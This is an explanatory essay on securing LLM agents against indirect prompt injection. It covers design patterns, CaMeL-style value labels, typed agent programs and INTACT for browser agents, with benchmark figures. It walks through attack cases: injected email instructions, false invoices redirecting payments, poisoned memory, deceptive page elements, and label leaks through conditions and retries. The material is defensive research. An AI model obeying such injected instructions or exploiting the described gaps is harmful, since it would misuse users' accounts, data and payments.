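The argument is convincing about what a model reads. In adaptive tests, where attackers keep adjusting their attempts to a known defence, many filter-style defences have failed. But a model can't send an email by itself. It writes a tool's name and some arguments, and an ordinary program parses them and runs the tool. That program can refuse a payment above a limit or a message to an unknown address, even if an attacker has persuaded the model to request it. The NCSC recommends this kind of safeguard, so its pessimism applies to the model but not necessarily to the whole agent.

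Rules on tool calls can also be badly written. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) describes a March 2026 fault in Claude Code, which checked only the first command in a line of joined commands against its list of forbidden ones. MySpace's filter similarly searched text without interpreting it as the browser would. A rule should work on the parsed command.

Even a parsed command doesn't show who chose its values. A request to send an email to `ana@office.example` looks the same whether the office worker or the stranger chose Ana as the recipient. To treat the two cases differently, the program needs a record of where each value came from.

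### Six design patterns

One solution is to limit what an agent can do after it reads untrusted input. Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, argue that the limits must make it impossible for that input to trigger a harmful action. They doubt that a general-purpose agent built on current models can offer reliable safety guarantees, so each of their six patterns makes the agent somewhat less flexible.

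| Pattern | How it works | What a hostile email can still do |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from a fixed list of actions and never sees the results | Nothing, because the model doesn't read it |
| Plan, then execute | The model fixes its list of tool calls before it reads any email | Change the content that a planned call sends |
| Map-reduce | A separate model call reads each email and returns something narrow, such as yes or no | Cause a wrong answer about itself |
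| Dual LLM | One model plans and uses tools; another reads the emails and has no tools | Change a value that the planner passes on unseen |
| Code, then execute | The model writes a complete program, which then runs on the emails | Change the values in the program |
| Context minimisation | The program removes the user's request before the model writes its answer | Act as before, since this pattern is for attacks in the request itself |

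Suppose the worker asks the assistant to collect this month's invoices and send them to the accounts department. With map-reduce, the stranger could make the model count a sales offer as an invoice. But the stranger could get the same result by sending a false invoice, and so gains very little from the injection.

Planning in advance gives weaker protection. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe a user who asks an assistant to send the day's schedule to a manager. If the assistant plans its actions before reading the calendar, instructions hidden in an entry can't add a second email or change the recipient, but they can rewrite the whole schedule.

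### How CaMeL labels values

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues at Google and ETH Zurich published in 2025, combines the dual-LLM and code patterns with labels on every value. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe the design in detail. Suppose the worker asks the assistant to send the reference number of today's transfer to `ana@office.example`. The planning model might write this program:

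```
emails = read_inbox("today")
number = ask_reader("Find the transfer's reference number", emails)
send_email(to="ana@office.example", body=number)
```

1. The planning model writes the program from the worker's request alone. It never sees the emails, so the stranger can't influence which tools the program calls.
2. An interpreter, an ordinary program, runs the first line. It labels the emails with their sources and with the people who may read them.
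3. The reading model, which has no tools, looks for the number. The stranger's paragraph may fool it into returning something else, but the interpreter stores whatever it returns as a value, with labels that record its origin.
4. Before sending anything, the interpreter runs a policy, a short function that inspects the tool's arguments and their labels. The address came from the worker's request, which CaMeL trusts. If Ana may read the number, the policy allows the email.

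The labels matter most when an attacker doesn't need to change the plan. Suppose the worker asks the assistant to pay a supplier's latest invoice, and the stranger has sent a false one. The program would make the right calls in the right order but send the money to the stranger's bank account. A policy that requires the account number to come from a trusted source would stop the payment. It would also stop payment of genuine invoices, because suppliers usually send their account numbers by email too.

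### Labels and security types

CaMeL's labels resemble the security types in Google's web templates, and Christoph Kern, who described those types, co-wrote the CaMeL paper. In both designs, a dangerous operation accepts a string only if it comes with evidence about the string that only trusted code can supply.

But a tool call needs different evidence that a value is safe. A sanitiser can turn a stranger's markup into `SafeHtml`, because cleaned markup is harmless whoever wrote it. No function can clean a bank account number, because a stranger's number is as well formed as the supplier's. With Google's types, reviewers didn't have to trace where a value came from. For tool calls the origin does matter, so CaMeL's interpreter has to trace it automatically.

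Zhou and colleagues bring the two ideas closer together in ELBA, a system in which the agent writes its actions as programs in Haskell, a language with unusually strict types, and a compiler checks each program before it runs. In one example, an agent compiles bibliographies. Only the function that fetches entries from DBLP, a database of computer science papers, can create a value of type `Trusted`, and the function that writes to the file accepts only `Trusted` values. In a test with 100 topics, none of the agent's 925 citations had a wrong author, year or identifier, compared with 19 of 1,002 from an ordinary agent with web search. The type guarantees that an entry came from DBLP, but not that it is relevant to the topic.

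*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) does something similar in the programming language Scala. Its library keeps classified data in a wrapper, so the agent's code can handle the data without it reaching the model.

Google's types can also be bypassed with an unchecked conversion, which a security engineer has to review. In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) add a comparable operation, `endorse`, which lets a program mark an outside value as trusted. Endorsements are easy to find in the code, but in their agent, Randori, the planning model writes them itself. It does so before any email can influence it, but it could still endorse too much.

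### Tasks completed and costs

Most of the measurements use AgentDojo, a benchmark in which an agent does office and banking tasks with simulated tools while attackers plant instructions in the data. *SecureClaw* (2026) reports a run of CaMeL on the whole benchmark. None of the 629 attacks succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 ordinary tasks.

| Test | CaMeL | Newer system |
|---|---|---|
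| 97 tasks from the whole benchmark | 29 | SecureClaw: 59 |
| 21 Slack tasks, policies on | 4 to 6, depending on the model | ELBA: 8 to 10 |
| 21 Slack tasks, policies off | 13 to 17 | ELBA: 14 to 18 |
| 48 runs of banking tasks, policies on | 18 | Randori: about twice as many |

Researchers presenting a rival system produced each row and may have put less effort into getting good results from CaMeL. But in the Slack results, both systems complete far fewer tasks with their policies on than off, because many legitimate tasks require an action that depends on outside data.

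The choice of policy strongly affects how many tasks an agent completes. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) compares two policies on the same enforcement system. The agent completed 62.5% of tasks under rules about the origin of individual arguments, and 33.2% under a stricter policy that followed labels through everything the agent read. It completed 83.7% with only the benchmark's built-in defence.

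CaMeL is also slow. Across 200 AgentDojo cases, *ToolFence* (2026) measured an average of 81.7 seconds with CaMeL and 6.31 seconds without a defence, and attributed the difference to repeated code generation and restricted execution. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) found that CaMeL used 2.82 times as much input text and 2.73 times as much output for the median task. ELBA took about three times as long as CaMeL because its agent calls the model again after reading data.

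A perfect security score on AgentDojo may be weak evidence that a system's design is secure. When Zhou and colleagues ran the standard attacks on four 2026 models, every model resisted all 105, even with the policies off. They then simulated the worst case by having ELBA's models carry out the injected instructions. Up to 42% of attacks succeeded without the policies and none succeeded with them, which is much better evidence that the policies work. Their policy also matches the NCSC's recommendation that a model that reads somebody's data should have no more privileges than that person.

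Randori resisted all but two of 1,296 attacked runs. In both failures, the task was to read a file and follow the payment instructions in it, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. According to Garby and colleagues, CaMeL's developers had found the same case and excluded it from the attacks CaMeL is meant to stop. If a user asks an agent to follow payment instructions in a document, anyone who controls the document can change the payment, and labels can prevent this only by blocking the whole task.

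### Where the labels go wrong

A label is only useful if the interpreter attaches it to everything the data influences. Garby and colleagues found that the way CaMeL handles conditions allows a kind of leak researchers had known about since the 1970s. Suppose a variable starts as "rich", and the program changes it to "poor" only if the user's bank balance is low. If the balance is high, the variable never changes, so CaMeL doesn't label it as private. Its value now reveals that the balance is high, and CaMeL lets the program send it to anyone.

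CaMeL can also leak through its retries. If a policy blocks a program because of a private value, an observer may learn one fact about that value from the failure. CaMeL then tries again in an outer loop that doesn't track labels, so repeated failures could reveal the whole value. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) reports that an October 2026 extension of CaMeL to several cooperating agents inherits the gap in conditions. Garby and colleagues wrote their own interpreter in Lean and proved that its labels don't have such gaps, although the proof doesn't cover values that a program endorses.

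CaMeLoT, a system by Nikolaou and colleagues, checks the plan before any tool runs, which reduces the need for retries during a task. It maps every path the plan's program could take and searches for one that breaks a rule, such as a payment without approval. It describes any such path to the planning model, which can then repair the plan. This feedback can't contain an attacker's words because the agent hasn't read anything yet. But the map is approximate, so CaMeLoT may reject some safe plans, and rules that depend on actual values still have to be checked when the program runs.

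Deciding how much text should share a label is also difficult, as *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) points out. A single summary of the twelve emails would have to carry the stranger's label throughout, whereas separate summaries could each have their own label.

Memory makes this harder because a stored value can cause harm days later. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) gives the example of an agent that saves the details of a false invoice on Monday and is asked on Tuesday to pay "the invoice we discussed yesterday". SPA stores each value with its label and shows the planning model only a description of it, whereas Claude's memory summary enters every conversation as text that the model reads. With SPA, attack success fell to zero on AgentDojo and to 0.2% on a version with several linked requests. The share of ordinary tasks completed on AgentDojo also fell, from 53% to 29%, mainly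 because the checks refused actions that used outside data.

### Browser agents and the same-origin policy

An agent that operates a browser reads pages containing content from many parties. The same-origin policy stops an advertiser's frame from reading the shop page around it. But an agent usually receives the whole page as one text or screenshot, with the advertisement and the shop's checkout button together. If the agent follows an instruction in the advertisement, it can read the shopping basket and press the button using the user's login. Brave, a browser company that Iqbal quotes, calls the same-origin policy "effectively useless" once an agent follows such instructions.

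CaMeL doesn't fit this setting well, because its planning model can't look at the page. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) had the planner write a program that covered every situation it could anticipate, such as a cookie notice or a failed login. The average plan had about 40 branches, compared with fewer than four on AgentDojo. The agent retained up to 57% of the performance of leading models on OSWorld, a benchmark of ordinary computer tasks.

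An attacker couldn't add steps to these plans but could influence which branch the agent took. For example, an advertisement that looked like a cookie notice could make the agent click through to the attacker's site. Policies are hard to write here, because a command to click at certain coordinates doesn't show what the click will do. Foerster and colleagues tried checking the page's code and asking another model, and designed attacks against both. Another system, SPIDES, instead carries labels from page elements to checks on clicking and typing. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026) describes it briefly.

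In October 2026 Iqbal, a researcher at Washington University in St. Louis, proposed restoring the boundaries between a page's owners. Browsers don't normally keep enough information to do this. If an advertiser's script adds a button to a shop's own page, the browser treats the button as the shop's. Iqbal recorded which script had created or changed each element on the home pages of 1,270 sites, and found that the browser attributed 58.7% of third-party elements to the site. For third-party elements that accept text or submit forms, the figure was over 90%. Google's Chrome agent hides frames that come from unrelated origins, but according to Iqbal it would treat the misattributed elements as part of the site.

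Iqbal's system, INTACT, uses this record in three steps:

1. It notes who wrote each element and what the element can do. A link can open a page, for example, but an ordinary heading can't do anything.
2. It divides the page into chunks, picks the most relevant one, and shows the model its elements one at a time. The model also sees the user's request and a log of earlier steps, but no text from other elements.
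3. An ordinary program carries out the model's decision, but only on that element and only if the element allows the action. It asks the user before acting on anything a third party wrote.

Suppose an insurance comparison page contains a note instructing AI assistants to open Insurer B's quote. The note may mislead the model, but at that moment the model can act only on the note itself, which contains nothing to click.

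To test the design instead of the model's resistance, Iqbal told the model to obey injected instructions and planted one attack on each of 1,091 real pages. A conventional planner followed 73.1% of the attacks. With INTACT, 12.8% got through the planner, and each would only have led to a request for the user's consent. Most of these used a form field that the attacker had added to the page, with a "Continue" button that looked like a normal next step. A careless user might approve the click, but INTACT never copied private data into such a field, because the model couldn't see the data and the field together.

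In ordinary use, INTACT would have asked for consent in 112 of the 1,091 tasks. Iqbal reports that isolation disrupted 3.7% of tasks. That may understate the loss of usefulness in practice, since a model acting as judge rated 10% of INTACT's plans unsuitable, compared with 4.9% of the conventional planner's. Planning took 83 seconds instead of 2.5, although running the steps in parallel could remove most of the delay. INTACT's planner also can't compare values in different elements, so it couldn't find the cheapest of several quotes.

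INTACT trusts everything the site's own server and scripts deliver, which on a webmail page includes the stranger's email. The paragraph addressed to AI systems still couldn't make the agent press "Send" elsewhere on the page. But INTACT would treat a link in the email as the mail site's own and could open it without asking the worker.
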